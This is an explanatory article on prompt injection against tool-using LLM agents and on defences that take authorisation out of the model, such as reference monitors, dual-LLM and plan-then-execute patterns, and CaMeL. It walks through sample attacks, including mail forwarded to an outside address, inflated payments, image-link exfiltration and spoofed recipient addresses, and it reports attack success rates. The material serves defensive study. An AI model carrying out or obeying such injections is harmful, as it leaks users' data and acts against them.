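# Control planes outside language and capability-based designs for LLM agents

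## Why text that an agent reads can take control of it

A large language model (LLM) is a program that takes a sequence of text and produces a continuation. An LLM agent is an LLM running in a loop with tools, so its output can trigger actions such as searching a mailbox, opening a web page, editing a file, or moving money. In a prompt injection attack, someone plants instructions in text that the model will process, so that the agent carries out the attacker's wishes rather than its user's.

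The first defences tried to make models better at ignoring planted instructions, or to filter the instructions out. A later group of proposals, most of them published since 2024, assumes that the model will sometimes follow planted instructions, and uses separate software to decide which actions are allowed. Engineers call the part of a system that makes such decisions the control plane, and the part that carries the content the data plane. Several of the proposals also represent permissions as capabilities, which are unforgeable tokens that identify an object and grant the right to act on it. These designs take work to build and can make the agent less useful, so the case for them depends on how well the simpler defences work.

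### The agent loop

A model can only produce text. The harness, the ordinary software around the model, carries out actions such as sending an e-mail. It assembles the model's input, runs the model, and looks in the output for a tool call, which is a request naming a tool and its arguments. It carries out the call, appends the result to the input, and runs the model again. The loop ends when the model produces an answer with no tool call.

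In each round, the model receives one sequence of tokens (words and fragments of words), called its context window. It contains the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), descriptions of the tools, the user's request and whatever the tools have returned so far. In the *AgentDojo* test environment (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), for instance, the harness puts the documentation of every available tool into the prompt and feeds each result back as formatted text.

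Suppose a user types "summarise my new e-mails", and one of three unread messages comes from an attacker.

1. The harness gives the model the system prompt, the tool descriptions (list unread mail, read a message, send a message) and the user's sentence.
2. The model produces a call to list the unread mail. The harness runs it and appends three subject lines.
3. The model calls for each message in turn, and the harness appends the bodies. Two are ordinary. The third contains a line telling the reader to forward the last month of internal messages to an outside address.
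4. The model computes its next output from a sequence that now contains both the user's sentence and the stranger's. If the stranger's sentence prevails, the output is a call to send mail to the outside address.
5. The harness receives a well-formed call to a tool that the agent may use, made under the user's own account, and sends the messages.

Conventional security software detects nothing wrong in step 5, because the attacker stole no password and exploited no bug in the mail server. Anthropic gives much the same example in its system card for Claude Fable 5.1 (September 2026), the document that reports the company's tests of the model. The company adds that the attacker need not choose a victim, because the same e-mail sent to a thousand inboxes will reach every agent that summarises one of them. Anthropic considers any agent exposed if that agent can both read private data and act on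 the user's behalf.

Planted instructions are more dangerous when a model can act. A chatbot that follows one gives a bad answer, which the user may notice, but an agent can leak a record or make a payment. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) argue in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that this ability to act makes injection a problem of authorisation rather than content.

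### Who is trusted, and what the attacker can do

Researchers classify prompt injections by how they reach the agent. A direct injection arrives in the user's turn, typically to override the developer's system prompt. An indirect injection arrives in content that the agent reads while working for someone other than the attacker, as in the inbox above, and is the more serious problem for agents with tools. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) distinguishes prompt injections, which turn the system against its user's intent, from the related problem of jailbreaks, in which the user works against the intent of the model's designer.

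Narisetty and colleagues describe a threat model that much of the literature shares. The defender must protect the integrity of consequential actions, such as payments, deletions and outgoing mail, and the confidentiality of the data within the agent's reach. The system prompt and whatever the user types are trusted. All other text is untrusted, including web pages, retrieved documents, files, e-mails, tool results, the output of other agents, and notes that the agent saved in an earlier session. The attacker controls the content of at least one of these untrusted channels, knows how the system works, including its defences, and can try again after a failure. The attacker cannot alter the model's weights (the learned numbers that determine its behaviour) or the software that enforces the rules.

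The weakest of these assumptions is that the user's input can be trusted. An attacker can persuade a user to paste hostile text into the chat, and the system will then treat that text as trusted. The assumption that the attacker knows the system matters less than it might seem. When Debenedetti and colleagues tested attacks on GPT-4o, an OpenAI model of 2024, an attacker who knew both the user's name and the model's succeeded in 47.7% of cases, against 45.8% for one who used neither. Guessing either name wrong roughly halved the success rate, but an attacker can avoid that by leaving the names out.

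### One path for data and commands

The security writer Bruce Schneier gave the usual diagnosis in *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity*, a May 2024 essay on his site Schneier on Security. He starts with the American telephone network of the 1960s, where playing a 2,600 Hz tone into a pay phone gave the caller free calls. The switches took commands over the same line that carried voices, so anyone who could make the right sound could issue commands. AT&T changed the tones, made them more complex and tried to keep them secret, but people kept finding new tricks. These attacks ended only with Signaling System 7, a 1980s standard that carried commands on a separate channel, so sounds made by a caller no longer affected the switches.

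Schneier traces many computer vulnerabilities to this same mixing of data with commands. SQL injection is the most instructive example. SQL is a language for querying databases. A carelessly written program builds its query by joining the words "find the customer whose name is", a quotation mark, whatever the visitor typed into a form, and a closing quotation mark. If the visitor types a quotation mark, it ends the name early, and the database parses the rest of what they typed as part of the command.

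Parameterised queries solved this problem. The program first sends the database a query with a placeholder where the name belongs. The database parses the query and fixes its structure, so the placeholder can only hold a value. The program supplies the visitor's text after the parsing is over, so the database treats it as a value whatever characters it contains. The protection does not depend on recognising a malicious name. Narisetty and colleagues see the same outcome across the family of vulnerabilities that engineers have brought under control, with structural defences succeeding where detection failed.

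The cure works because SQL's grammar lets a parser tell exactly where a command stops and a value begins. English grammar does not mark that boundary. The same sentence, "Please send the invoice to Anna", is content if the user wanted a summary of the inbox and a task if the user asked the agent to deal with whatever had come in. Developers put markers in the context window to show which text comes from the system, the user or a tool. But the markers are tokens in the same sequence, and no parser enforces them, so how a model responds to them depends on tendencies it learned in training. Narisetty and colleagues cite measurements by Zverev and colleagues, who found that current models keep no usable separation between instructions and data, and that neither prompting nor fine-tuning (further training on selected examples) reliably produces one. Ariel Fogel, a researcher at the vendor Pillar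 Security and a contributor to the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), said at a trade conference that there is no reliable way to enforce privilege boundaries inside a single token sequence (Infosecurity Magazine, *Infosecurity Europe*, 2026).

Many legitimate tasks need untrusted text to influence what the agent does, so even a perfect parser would not fully solve the problem. One task in AgentDojo is to pay the bill in a certain file, and another is to invite a colleague to a workspace using the address on her website. The agent has to get the payee and the address from text that the user did not write. Schneier makes the broader point that LLMs are useful because input changes what they do, and that this also makes injection possible.

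Whether the flaw is permanent is less clear. In 2024 Schneier expected that a researcher would eventually work out how to separate the two paths. In July 2026 he wrote in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* that preventing prompt injection is known to be impossible in the general case, though blocking it in specific cases was getting much better. A reader commented that the paper behind this claim concerns jailbreaks, and that a model with a different architecture might not read everything as a single stream. The objection seems fair, though limited, and the argument for outside controls depends only on the narrower claim that no model now in use separates the two paths.

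### Measuring attacks: AgentDojo

Most of the figures in this field come from AgentDojo. Debenedetti and colleagues built four simulated environments: an office workspace with e-mail and calendar, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. Each has a set of user tasks, such as counting the day's appointments, and a set of injection tasks, which are goals for an attacker, such as sending money to a certain account. Pairing every user task with every injection task in the same environment gives the security cases:

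| Environment | User tasks | Injection tasks | Security cases |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 97 | 27 | 629 |

The benchmark has grown since: *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) puts it at more than 900 pairs.

In each case the attacker's text sits where untrusted content would appear, in the body of an e-mail or on a web page. Ordinary code then checks the environment to see whether the money moved or the appointment exists. Debenedetti and colleagues decided against using a second model to judge the outcome, because an injection that hijacks the agent might hijack the judge too.

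Debenedetti and colleagues measure three quantities. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when nobody is attacking. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which it completes the user's task with no harmful side effect. The targeted attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the attacker's goal is achieved. This rate should be read alongside utility, because an agent that does nothing would score zero. In 2024 the more capable models were often easier to attack, which Debenedetti and colleagues explain by noting that weak models often failed to carry out the attacker's task even after the injection had worked. Success rates also varied widely between tasks. Against GPT-4o, attacks succeeded in 92% of the Slack cases, while one travel attack, which required two unrelated malicious actions, never succeeded.

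AgentDojo's stock attacks are fixed texts, although researchers can add their own. A defence can therefore do well by blocking those particular texts.

### How far training and filtering have got

Nasr and colleagues attacked twelve published defences with methods adapted to each one, using automated search, reinforcement learning (training an attacking model by rewarding its successes) and a public competition with more than 500 participants. Attack success had originally been reported as near zero for most of the defences, but it rose above 90% for most of them under these attacks. Two of the defences are aimed at jailbreaks, and the other ten address injection and fall into four families.

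| Family | How the defence is meant to work | Attack success under adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|
| Prompting (Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching) | Marks off the trusted text, or repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% for both |
| Training (StruQ, MetaSecAlign) | Fine-tunes the model on examples of attacks | Every case tested for StruQ; 96% for MetaSecAlign |
| Filtering (Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor, PIGuard) | A separate classifier screens text for injections | Above 90% for three; 71% for PIGuard |
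| Secret knowledge (Data Sentinel, MELON) | Runs a hidden check that the attacker cannot see | Every case for Data Sentinel; 76% for MELON, 95% once the attacker knew its design |

The two prompting defences had let through as little as 1% of AgentDojo's stock attacks, and MetaSecAlign had let through 2%. Both sets of results come from the same systems facing different attackers.

Nasr and colleagues warn against ranking the defences by these figures, since they tested each one on the benchmarks used in its original paper. They also gave the attackers ample computing power, because they wanted to know whether a defence could be broken at all, not how much computing that would take. They add that filters are still of some use against careless attackers, but the detector that Debenedetti and colleagues tried raised so many false alarms that the agent's utility fell sharply. On a subset of the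 scenarios, automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human participants collectively succeeded every time.

Those results date from October 2025, and the laboratories have since made progress. The fullest recent figures are in Anthropic's September 2026 card. The security firm Gray Swan ran a benchmark of 1,804 attacks, collected from public competitions, across 37 scenarios. Against Claude Fable 5.1, 0.1% of single attempts succeeded, and an attacker with fifteen attempts succeeded 1.0% of the time. The fifteen-attempt success rate was 9.2% against Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash, the best model from another company, and between 24% and 53% against most others. Anthropic published these comparisons itself, and the test conditions differed somewhat between companies, but the gap is large.

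The same card also includes much worse results. Gray Swan's second tool, Shade, is an automated attacker that learns from its failures. In 2026 the firm trained a stronger version for coding tasks. Shade makes 200 attempts at each of 40 scenarios. The last column below adds Anthropic's probes, a safeguard that inspects tool results before the model acts on them.

| Model, with extended reasoning | Benchmark, one attempt | Benchmark, within 15 attempts | Stronger Shade, share of attempts | Stronger Shade, with probes |
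|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 1.0% | 56.87% | 12.80% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 6.5% | 86.87% | 34.09% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 4.8% | 90.93% | 18.21% |

Anthropic reasonably calls this test highly permissive. Gray Swan optimised the attacker on the same scenarios in which it then ran, whereas a real attacker does not know the target deployment and risks detection with each attempt. In the first row, a safety filter for hacking requests diverted about 64% of Fable 5.1's traffic to an older model, Opus 4.8, and all the successful attacks came through that model. None succeeded in the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself, which is encouraging. But Gray Swan trained the earlier version of Shade against older Claude models and then ran it unchanged on the newer ones. If it trained the stronger version in the same way, the result would show that attacks developed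 against older models transfer poorly, which is weaker evidence than resistance to an attacker working on Fable 5.1 directly.

The results for Opus 5 show most clearly how much an attack's success rate depends on the attacker. In its July 2026 system card, Anthropic reported that the earlier version of Shade succeeded in 0.56% of attempts against the model in coding tasks. The September card put this rate at 2.68%, in runs that included diversions to the older model for the first time. The stronger version of Shade then reached 90.93%.

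The Decoder covered the July card under the headline *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, because no attack had succeeded in any of 129 browser scenarios. Opus 5 achieved that result with auto mode on, a setting that combines the probes with a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls. Without those safeguards, 3.70% of attempts succeeded, down from 31.5% for Opus 4.8.

OpenAI has published less data that outsiders can compare. Its safety overview for GPT-6 Astra (September 2026) describes the model as significantly more robust to injection than its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol. On the Gray Swan benchmark as it stood in July, an attacker could beat GPT-5.6 Sol within fifteen attempts 20.0% of the time. VentureBeat noted that for the earlier GPT-5.5, OpenAI had reported results for only one attack surface, its connectors to outside services, against attacks it already knew.

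Even when a single attack rarely succeeds, an attacker can keep trying. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*. For Opus 5 on the Gray Swan benchmark, *p* is 0.4%, so the formula gives 5.8% for fifteen attempts, a little above the measured 4.8%. Real success rates rise more slowly than the formula predicts, presumably because some scenarios resist nearly every attempt while others fail at once. For an older model, Claude Opus 4.5, Narisetty and colleagues quote success rates in coding tasks of 4.7% after one attempt, 33.6% after ten and 63.0% after a hundred. They argue that such a defence reduces the number of incidents but does not set a bound on them.

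OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". Auto mode already provides part of the defense, since its second layer checks outgoing actions as well as incoming text. But that layer is a classifier, and a model that screens for injections is itself vulnerable to them, as OWASP's guidance also notes. A reference monitor, a small piece of ordinary code that checks every tool call against a written policy, could block the forwarded mail in step 5 however persuasive the stranger's sentence was.

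## What it means to move control out of language

An agent's control plane consists of four decisions: which step comes next, which tool may run, which arguments the call may include, and where data may go. In the standard agent loop, the model makes all four when it writes a tool call. Pupneja's *Separating Control and Data Planes for Safe Agentic Browsing* cites a case in which text hidden behind a Reddit spoiler tag led a browser agent to leak two-factor login codes.

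Security systems normally separate choosing an action from deciding whether it is authorised, but agents commonly merge the two, as Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao point out in *AgentCap* (2026). *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes an alternative in which the model only proposes a call. Software called the policy decision point then applies the rules, and separate software called the policy enforcement point allows or blocks the call. *Can We Rely on Language Models to Orchestrate Services* (2026) distinguishes two further powers, carrying out an action with privileged access and recovering from it afterwards. A model can therefore write a complete repair plan for a failing server while other components approve and run it.

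Taking authorisation away from the model does not make its choices better. *ResidualAuth* (2026), a benchmark for agents whose permissions can be revoked, grades the model's proposal separately from the proposal's effect. Even if a gateway stops an unauthorised message, the model was still wrong to try to send it.

### A test for non-linguistic control

A control decision is non-linguistic if a mechanism computes it from structured state, and no wording in the model's context can alter that mechanism. Structured state means fields with a fixed type and meaning, such as a tool's name, a recipient's address, the company directory, or a log of earlier calls.

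Ordinary code can enforce a rule such as "send mail only to addresses in the company directory" by comparing the recipient in each proposed call with the directory. A stranger's e-mail may lead the model to propose a call, and may even determine the recipient, but it cannot change the comparison or the directory. The code allows or blocks the call based only on its fields and the current state, regardless of why the model proposed it.

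The test concerns how a system reaches a decision, so a bad decision can still pass. For example, the directory rule would let an injected instruction send the payroll file to every employee. A user's request does not supply the rule either. *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems* (2026) notes that "Handle my travel" does not specify a spending limit, whether a non-refundable ticket is acceptable, or who may see the traveller's identity documents. Someone has to translate the request into named resources, permitted operations and limits before code can enforce anything.

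### The reference monitor as a checklist

A sound rule does not protect against calls that bypass it. Narisetty and colleagues take their standard from James Anderson's 1972 study for the US Air Force, which introduced the reference monitor. The monitor must check every access, be tamperproof, and be small enough to verify.

Common agent frameworks do not check every access by default. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) traces tool calls through LangChain, LangGraph and LlamaIndex. The framework looks up the tool by the name the model produced, usually checks the format of the arguments, and runs the tool. A format check can confirm that a payment amount is a number, but not that the user is allowed to make the payment. Developers have to add any approval step themselves. Even checking every call may not be enough, because one approved action can set off effects in other tools,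 agents and outside services, as *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) notes.

Protection from tampering has to cover the monitor's code and the policy and state it consults. Some designers also hide the monitor's reasoning from the model. In most agent loops, the model receives a refusal as an error message and can then rephrase the command or try another tool. In *KAIJU* (2026), the planning model finishes before the gate runs, and the only feedback after a refusal is that a step failed. This makes probing harder, but it does little against the attacker usually assumed in this literature, who already knows the policy.

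A language model's clearest failing as a monitor is that nobody can verify what it will permit by inspecting its billions of weights. People can read and test a short program that matches calls against rules. Narisetty and colleagues add that verification is harder when a model writes the policy, even if the program enforcing it is simple.

### Steps, plans and policies

Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues (2026), in *Architecting Secure AI Agents*, a position paper from a group mostly at NVIDIA, give these ideas a compact notation. A step is a triple *e* = (*a*, *I*, *O*), where *a* is an action, *I* the objects it takes as input and *O* the objects it produces. A plan is a sequence of steps (*e*₁, …, *e*ₜ) or, more generally, a directed graph of them. For the task "summarise the most recent email from Alice and draft a reply", the plan might be:

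1. *e*₁ = (fetch the latest e-mail, sender Alice, message)
2. *e*₂ = (summarise, message, summary)
3. *e*₃ = (draft a reply, summary, draft)

A policy is a predicate π, a function that returns 1 if a step is allowed and 0 if it is not. It can depend on both the step and the history of earlier steps. Checking "transfer money only to verified contacts" requires the step and a contact list, while checking "send nothing outside the company after opening a confidential file" requires the history. If 𝒫 is the set of all possible plans, the plans permitted by the policy form a subset 𝒫_π.

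The plan describes how the agent might do the task, and the policy defines what the agent is allowed to do. If an attacker takes over the plan but the policy is still enforced, the agent can only follow plans in 𝒫_π, so its safety depends on how much harm those plans can do. Suppose the attacker in the Alice example adds a fourth step, *e*₄ = (send, {last month's messages, outside address}, sent mail). A policy that allows only fetching, summarising and drafting gives π(*e*₄) = 0, so the step never runs.

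Policies that look strict can still permit a large set of actions. Xiang and colleagues discuss a payment rule that requires the user to name the recipient. A user writes, "Pay Joe back for the bouquet of flowers he bought at Store XYZ", and the agent looks up the price on the web. The recipient passes the check, but a sentence planted on the web page can raise the amount, because the rule doesn't restrict the amount.

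### Prompts, judges and generated rules

A system prompt that forbids an action does not move control out of language, because the prohibition is still text that the model may not follow. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes written warnings as useful engineering practice but not as a hard security boundary.

A second model that judges each action also fails if it reads the same web pages and e-mails as the first, because an attacker can address it directly. Xiang and colleagues propose showing the judge only structured records, such as a proposed change to the plan, and asking it a narrow question. This gives an attacker much less opportunity to influence the judge, but a file name or web address in the record can still contain words the attacker chose, and a learned model still gives the verdict. The design is therefore better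 described as a restricted linguistic control than as a non-linguistic one.

If a model writes a rule file and code enforces it, whether control has moved out of language depends on when the model wrote the rules. Once the file is fixed, enforcement happens outside language. If the model wrote the file from the user's request alone, planted text could not have influenced the rules. But if the model can revise them after reading tool results, an attacker can use wording in a web page to change what the code allows.

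### Marking the source of each token

Another group of designs changes the model itself so that the harness can mark each token's source without adding text. A model first turns each token into a vector called an embedding. Normally the word "send" gets the same embedding whether the user or a stranger wrote it. *Instructional Segment Embedding* (2024) adds a learned vector for the source to each token's embedding, and *Stronger Enforcement of Instruction Hierarchy via Augmented Intermediate Representations* (2025) also injects this signal into later layers.

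*ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) uses a fixed rotation instead. For each data token, the software groups the entries of the embedding into pairs and rotates each pair by 90 degrees, so that (*x*, *y*) becomes (−*y*, *x*). The harness assigns the roles, so an attacker cannot turn data into instructions by imitating a delimiter. The researchers then fine-tuned several open models on ordinary instruction data, with no examples of attacks. Average attack success fell from 14.7% to 4.9% on one benchmark of injected text, but only from 45.6% to 28.1% on another.

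The remaining failures matter for a theoretical argument by Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*. They claim that a model which processes trusted and untrusted text in one shared representation cannot guarantee protection against injection. Part of the argument concerns how well anyone could recover a token's source from its internal vector. If trusted and untrusted vectors are equally common, the lowest achievable error rate is

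*P* = ½ (1 − TV),

where TV, the total variation distance, runs from 0 when the two kinds of vector have identical distributions to 1 when they do not overlap. Common words such as "the" appear in both kinds of text with the same embedding, so TV is below 1 and some error is unavoidable. For the deeper layers, Pant and colleagues assume an overlap rather than proving it.

ASIDE largely removes the overlap at the embedding layer. In one of the ASIDE models, a simple classifier separated instruction tokens from data tokens with 100% accuracy from the start of processing. Attacks still succeeded, so a model can clearly represent where a sentence came from and still follow it. The stronger part of Pant and colleagues' argument is therefore that untrusted text still enters the computation that produces tool calls, and that no finite training set can cover every way of rewording an attack. They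 exempt systems where an external policy engine makes the decision.

Later designs get much lower attack rates. *Semantic Overlays* (Penman, 2026) leaves the model's weights unchanged and trains small add-on networks that adjust the model's internal state wherever the harness has marked a passage as untrusted. The results below are for Qwen3.5-9B, a small open model.

| Attack | Success without the overlay | Success with the overlay |
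|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, fixed attacks | 12.8% | 0% |
| AlpacaFarm, fixed attacks | 99.0% | 0.5% |
| PIArena, a second model rewrites the injection | 97% | 10.8% |
| AlpacaFarm, automated search using the model's weights | Not reported | 72%, or 14% after further training against such attacks |

Penman notes that no input text can create or remove a mark, but the model learns how to respond to the mark, and the input influences that response. The marking therefore passes the test for non-linguistic control, but the decision about what to do with marked text does not.

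In *Origin Is All You Need*, Zhang, Huang and Gu (2026) modify attention, the operation by which a model draws on earlier tokens as it writes. They label each token with one of four sources and add a learned penalty when the assistant's own tokens attend to external content. They report near-zero attack success, and say the defence also works when attackers have full access to the weights. However, a finite penalty never reduces a token's weight to zero. A penalty of −5 on an attention score, for example, multiplies the weight, before normalisation, by *e*⁻⁵, or about 0.7%. An infinite penalty would create a hard barrier, but it would also stop the assistant's tokens from attending to a document the assistant was asked to summarise. Zhang and colleagues want external text to inform the output without exerting "instruction-level" influence on it, and that distinction depends on meaning, so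 the model has to learn it.

### Control signals read from hidden states

In *Multi-Head Latent Control*, Ghasemabadi, Chen and colleagues (2026) attach two small trained networks, called heads, to a model whose weights stay fixed. The heads read the model's hidden states, the internal vectors it computes while generating an answer, rather than its written output.

The Capability Head estimates whether the model is good enough for the task, so "capability" here means competence, not permissions. If the score is below 0.8, the system hands the task to a larger model. Otherwise the Resolution Head scores three options: asking for more information, calling a tool, and declining to answer. The system takes the highest-scoring option if its score exceeds 0.5, and otherwise lets the model answer directly. On AndroidWorld, a set of tasks on a simulated phone, a small model that could hand over to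 a larger one completed 60% of tasks at an API cost of $0.25. The larger model alone completed 58% and cost $2.70.

The two thresholds are ordinary code, but the scores compared with them come from a learned function of hidden states. Every sentence in the context can affect those states, including one written by an attacker. Ghasemabadi and colleagues built the system to cut costs and improve tool use, so this is not a failure by the system's own goals. But it shows that text can still influence a control signal that has been moved out of the text channel.

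### A control plane for coding agents

*A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (Madatha, 2026) presents Rel(AI)Build, which uses ordinary code throughout its enforcement layer. The system works on top of existing coding tools such as Claude Code and Cursor and applies its controls at three points.

1. When a developer installs an agent, the software checks the agent's declared tools against one of five permission tiers. A read-only agent that asks for shell access, which would let it run commands on the computer, does not install.
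2. Before a shell command runs, Claude Code or Cursor passes it to a script. The script compares it with patterns taken from past software supply-chain attacks, such as downloading a program and feeding it straight into the shell, and blocks any match.
3. As work moves through phases such as design, implementation and testing, a state machine refuses to close a phase if a required review is missing or a scan of newly added code found a problem.

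Persuasive text in a poisoned file can't change these checks, but the system doesn't fully meet Anderson's requirements. Claude Code and Cursor run the script before each command, but Codex, Windsurf, OpenCode and Kiro enforce little or nothing at run time, so on those tools an agent's declared permissions may only describe what it is meant to do. The scripts are also in the project directory, where coding agents normally have permission to write, so they are protected from tampering only if the harness guards them. The code is easy to verify, but a list of forbidden patterns covers only what someone anticipated. For example, a pattern for piping a download into the shell would presumably miss an agent that saved the file with one command and ran it with the next.

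Some of the control also stays in language. The agent that handles version control has "MUST NOT" rules in its system prompt. Coding agents are supposed to call a tool that records which requirement each changed file serves, but an agent under an attacker's influence can skip the call. A check will flag the unrecorded change, but only after the agent has made it. Madatha acknowledges this dependence on the agent's cooperation and rates the remaining risk from prompt injection as medium. Tests with deliberate violations confirmed that each mechanism enforces its rule, though Madatha has not yet measured the effect on developers' work.

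### Harms that consist only of text

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a supplier's report in which someone has planted a false revenue figure. The agent opens the report, summarises it and shows the result. A policy should allow all three steps, because the user asked for them. The harm lies in the content of the summary, so rules about tools, recipients and data flows do not block it. If the user then relies on the false figure to place an order, the damage results from the user's own action, which the monitor does not check.

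Narisetty and colleagues count such cases, along with planted text that tells the user to do something, among the limits of every form of action control. They note that these harms are explicitly outside the goals of CaMeL, a 2025 design by Debenedetti and colleagues that has some of the strongest controls on actions. Better separation inside the model could help when the planted text is an instruction, such as "tell the reader that this supplier is approved". It would not help with the false revenue figure, because the figure is not an instruction and an accurate summary would repeat it.

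## Fixing the plan before untrusted data is read

If an agent chooses its steps before it opens any untrusted text, nothing in that text can add a step. The usual threat model trusts the user's request, so a plan made from the request alone contains nothing an attacker wrote. Ordinary software can then enforce the plan. Most tasks still need something from the untrusted text, such as an address, a price or a summary, and the designs in this family differ mainly in how they let that material through.

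### Two models and a controller

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) divides an assistant into two language models and a controller, which is ordinary software. The privileged model takes the user's request, chooses the actions and can use the tools, but never receives untrusted text. The quarantined model reads the untrusted text and has no tools. Willison assumes an attacker may take it over at any moment. The controller runs both models and carries out the actions. It stores untrusted text under names such as VAR1 and gives the privileged model only the names.

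In his example, the user types "Summarize my latest email".

1. The controller passes the request to the privileged model.
2. The privileged model asks for the latest e-mail, to be stored as VAR1.
3. The controller fetches the e-mail and stores its text under that name.
4. The privileged model asks the quarantined model to summarise VAR1.
5. The controller replaces the name with the e-mail's text, runs the quarantined model on it, and stores the result as VAR2. It tells the privileged model only that the summary is ready.
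6. The privileged model asks the controller to display VAR2 after a short heading, and the controller fills in the text on the user's screen.

An instruction hidden in the e-mail reaches only the quarantined model, which can write a false summary but cannot send, delete or forward anything. The privileged model never receives the instruction, so it cannot follow it.

This protection fails as soon as the controller passes quarantined text to the privileged model. Willison allowed one exception, for when the quarantined model only sorts text into fixed categories. The controller can then check that the output is exactly one of the category names and pass it on. He worried that developers adding features would leak text to the privileged model by mistake, and he called his solution "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and worse to use.

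Displaying the quarantined model's output to the user can also leak data. If the model reads private mail together with an attacker's message, it can write an image link with the private data encoded in the address, and displaying the image sends the data to the attacker's server. Willison would therefore allow links and images only from approved sites. Even then, an attacker could use a poisoned summary to persuade the user to copy a block of encoded text into a website.

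### Plan-then-execute and its relatives

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) describe six patterns for building restricted agents, including the dual-LLM pattern. They doubt that general-purpose agents can offer reliable guarantees with current models. Instead, they propose giving an agent a narrower job and building it so that once it has read untrusted input, that input cannot trigger any consequential action.

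| Pattern | How it works | What an attacker can still influence |
|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Nothing through tool results |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes its tool calls before reading any untrusted data | The contents of those calls, such as the body of an e-mail |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a constrained answer, such as yes or no | How the agent treats the attacker's own document |
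| Dual LLM | A privileged model handles untrusted text only by name | The text stored under the names |
| Code-then-execute | The model writes a program that calls tools and quarantined models | The values that the program handles |
| Context-minimisation | The system removes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | The query already made from the prompt |

In plan-then-execute, an agent asked to "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe" commits to two calls before reading the calendar. The first reads today's entries, and the second e-mails John Doe, with the body left blank until the entries have been read. Someone who plants text in a calendar entry can change the body of the e-mail, but cannot add a third call or redirect the message.

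The protection is much weaker if the plan fixes only which tools the agent uses. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a file assistant that commits to using commands to find and move files. An injection could still lead it to find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. They prefer to give each file to a separate model that can return only a category, so an injection in a file can at worst cause that file to be misplaced.

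Fixing the plan does little to limit an agent when the task's steps don't depend on what the agent reads. "Notify my regular collaborators that I will be on vacation" needs only a loop, because the number of recipients is unknown at the start. Fixing the plan is more limiting for an agent that answers questions from a database. Such an agent normally writes a better query if the first result doesn't answer the question, but it can't do this if the model never sees results. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues argue from ten case studies of this kind and report no measurements.

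### The right steps with the wrong values

An attacker can affect what a plan does without changing any of its steps. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives a short example in which the plan reads the messages in a channel called "general", asks a quarantined model to extract Bob's e-mail address from them, and sends "Meeting at 3pm" to that address. Suppose an attacker can post in the channel.

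| Planned step | Normal run | Run with a planted message |
|---|---|---|
| Read the channel | Ordinary messages, one of which gives Bob's address | The same messages, plus one that gives the attacker's address as Bob's new one |
| Extract Bob's address | Bob's address | The attacker's address |
| Send "Meeting at 3pm" to the address | Bob receives the message | The attacker receives the message |

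The agent ran the three planned steps in the planned order, and the attack still worked. Sending a meeting time to the wrong address may not matter much, but the agent could have sent a contract with the same plan. Separating the two models doesn't help, because the privileged model handles the address only by variable name and can't detect that it is wrong. The planted message only needs to contain a false statement, not an instruction.

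### CaMeL: a program whose values carry tags

CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) addresses this weakness by recording where each value came from. Nikolaou et al. describe how it works.

1. A privileged model reads the user's request and writes the plan as a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls itself.
3. When the program needs something from untrusted text, it calls a quarantined model as it would call a function, and stores the answer in a variable.
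4. The interpreter tags every value with its sources and with the people who may read it. CaMeL's designers call these tags capabilities, which is not the usual sense of the word.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a Python function that examines the tool, its arguments and their tags, and allows or denies the call.

In the example above, the tag on the address would show that it came from the channel, so a policy that requires a trusted recipient would stop the message to the attacker. It would also stop the message in the normal run, because Bob's real address came from the same channel. The tag records where a value came from, and the interpreter cannot check whether the value is correct. *Better Privilege Separation for Agents by Restricting Data Types* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) notes that CaMeL can ask the user to approve such operations as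 they come up, and that frequent requests may tire the user.

The result also depends on which tags the policy checks. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) includes a CaMeL-style program that takes a recipient's address from an untrusted e-mail. The address kept its untrusted tag, but the program still sent the message because the policy checked only the subject and the body. CaMeL's rule for payments in AgentDojo has a similar gap. As Xiang and colleagues describe it, the recipient must come from the user alone and must be allowed to see all the details of the payment. The inflated flower price described earlier gets past this rule, but a user's request to pay a bill from a named sender is blocked when the payee's details are in the invoice.

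Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL, running on OpenAI's o3 model, completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. No injection succeeded within CaMeL's threat model. The loss of utility on this benchmark was modest, but CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens.

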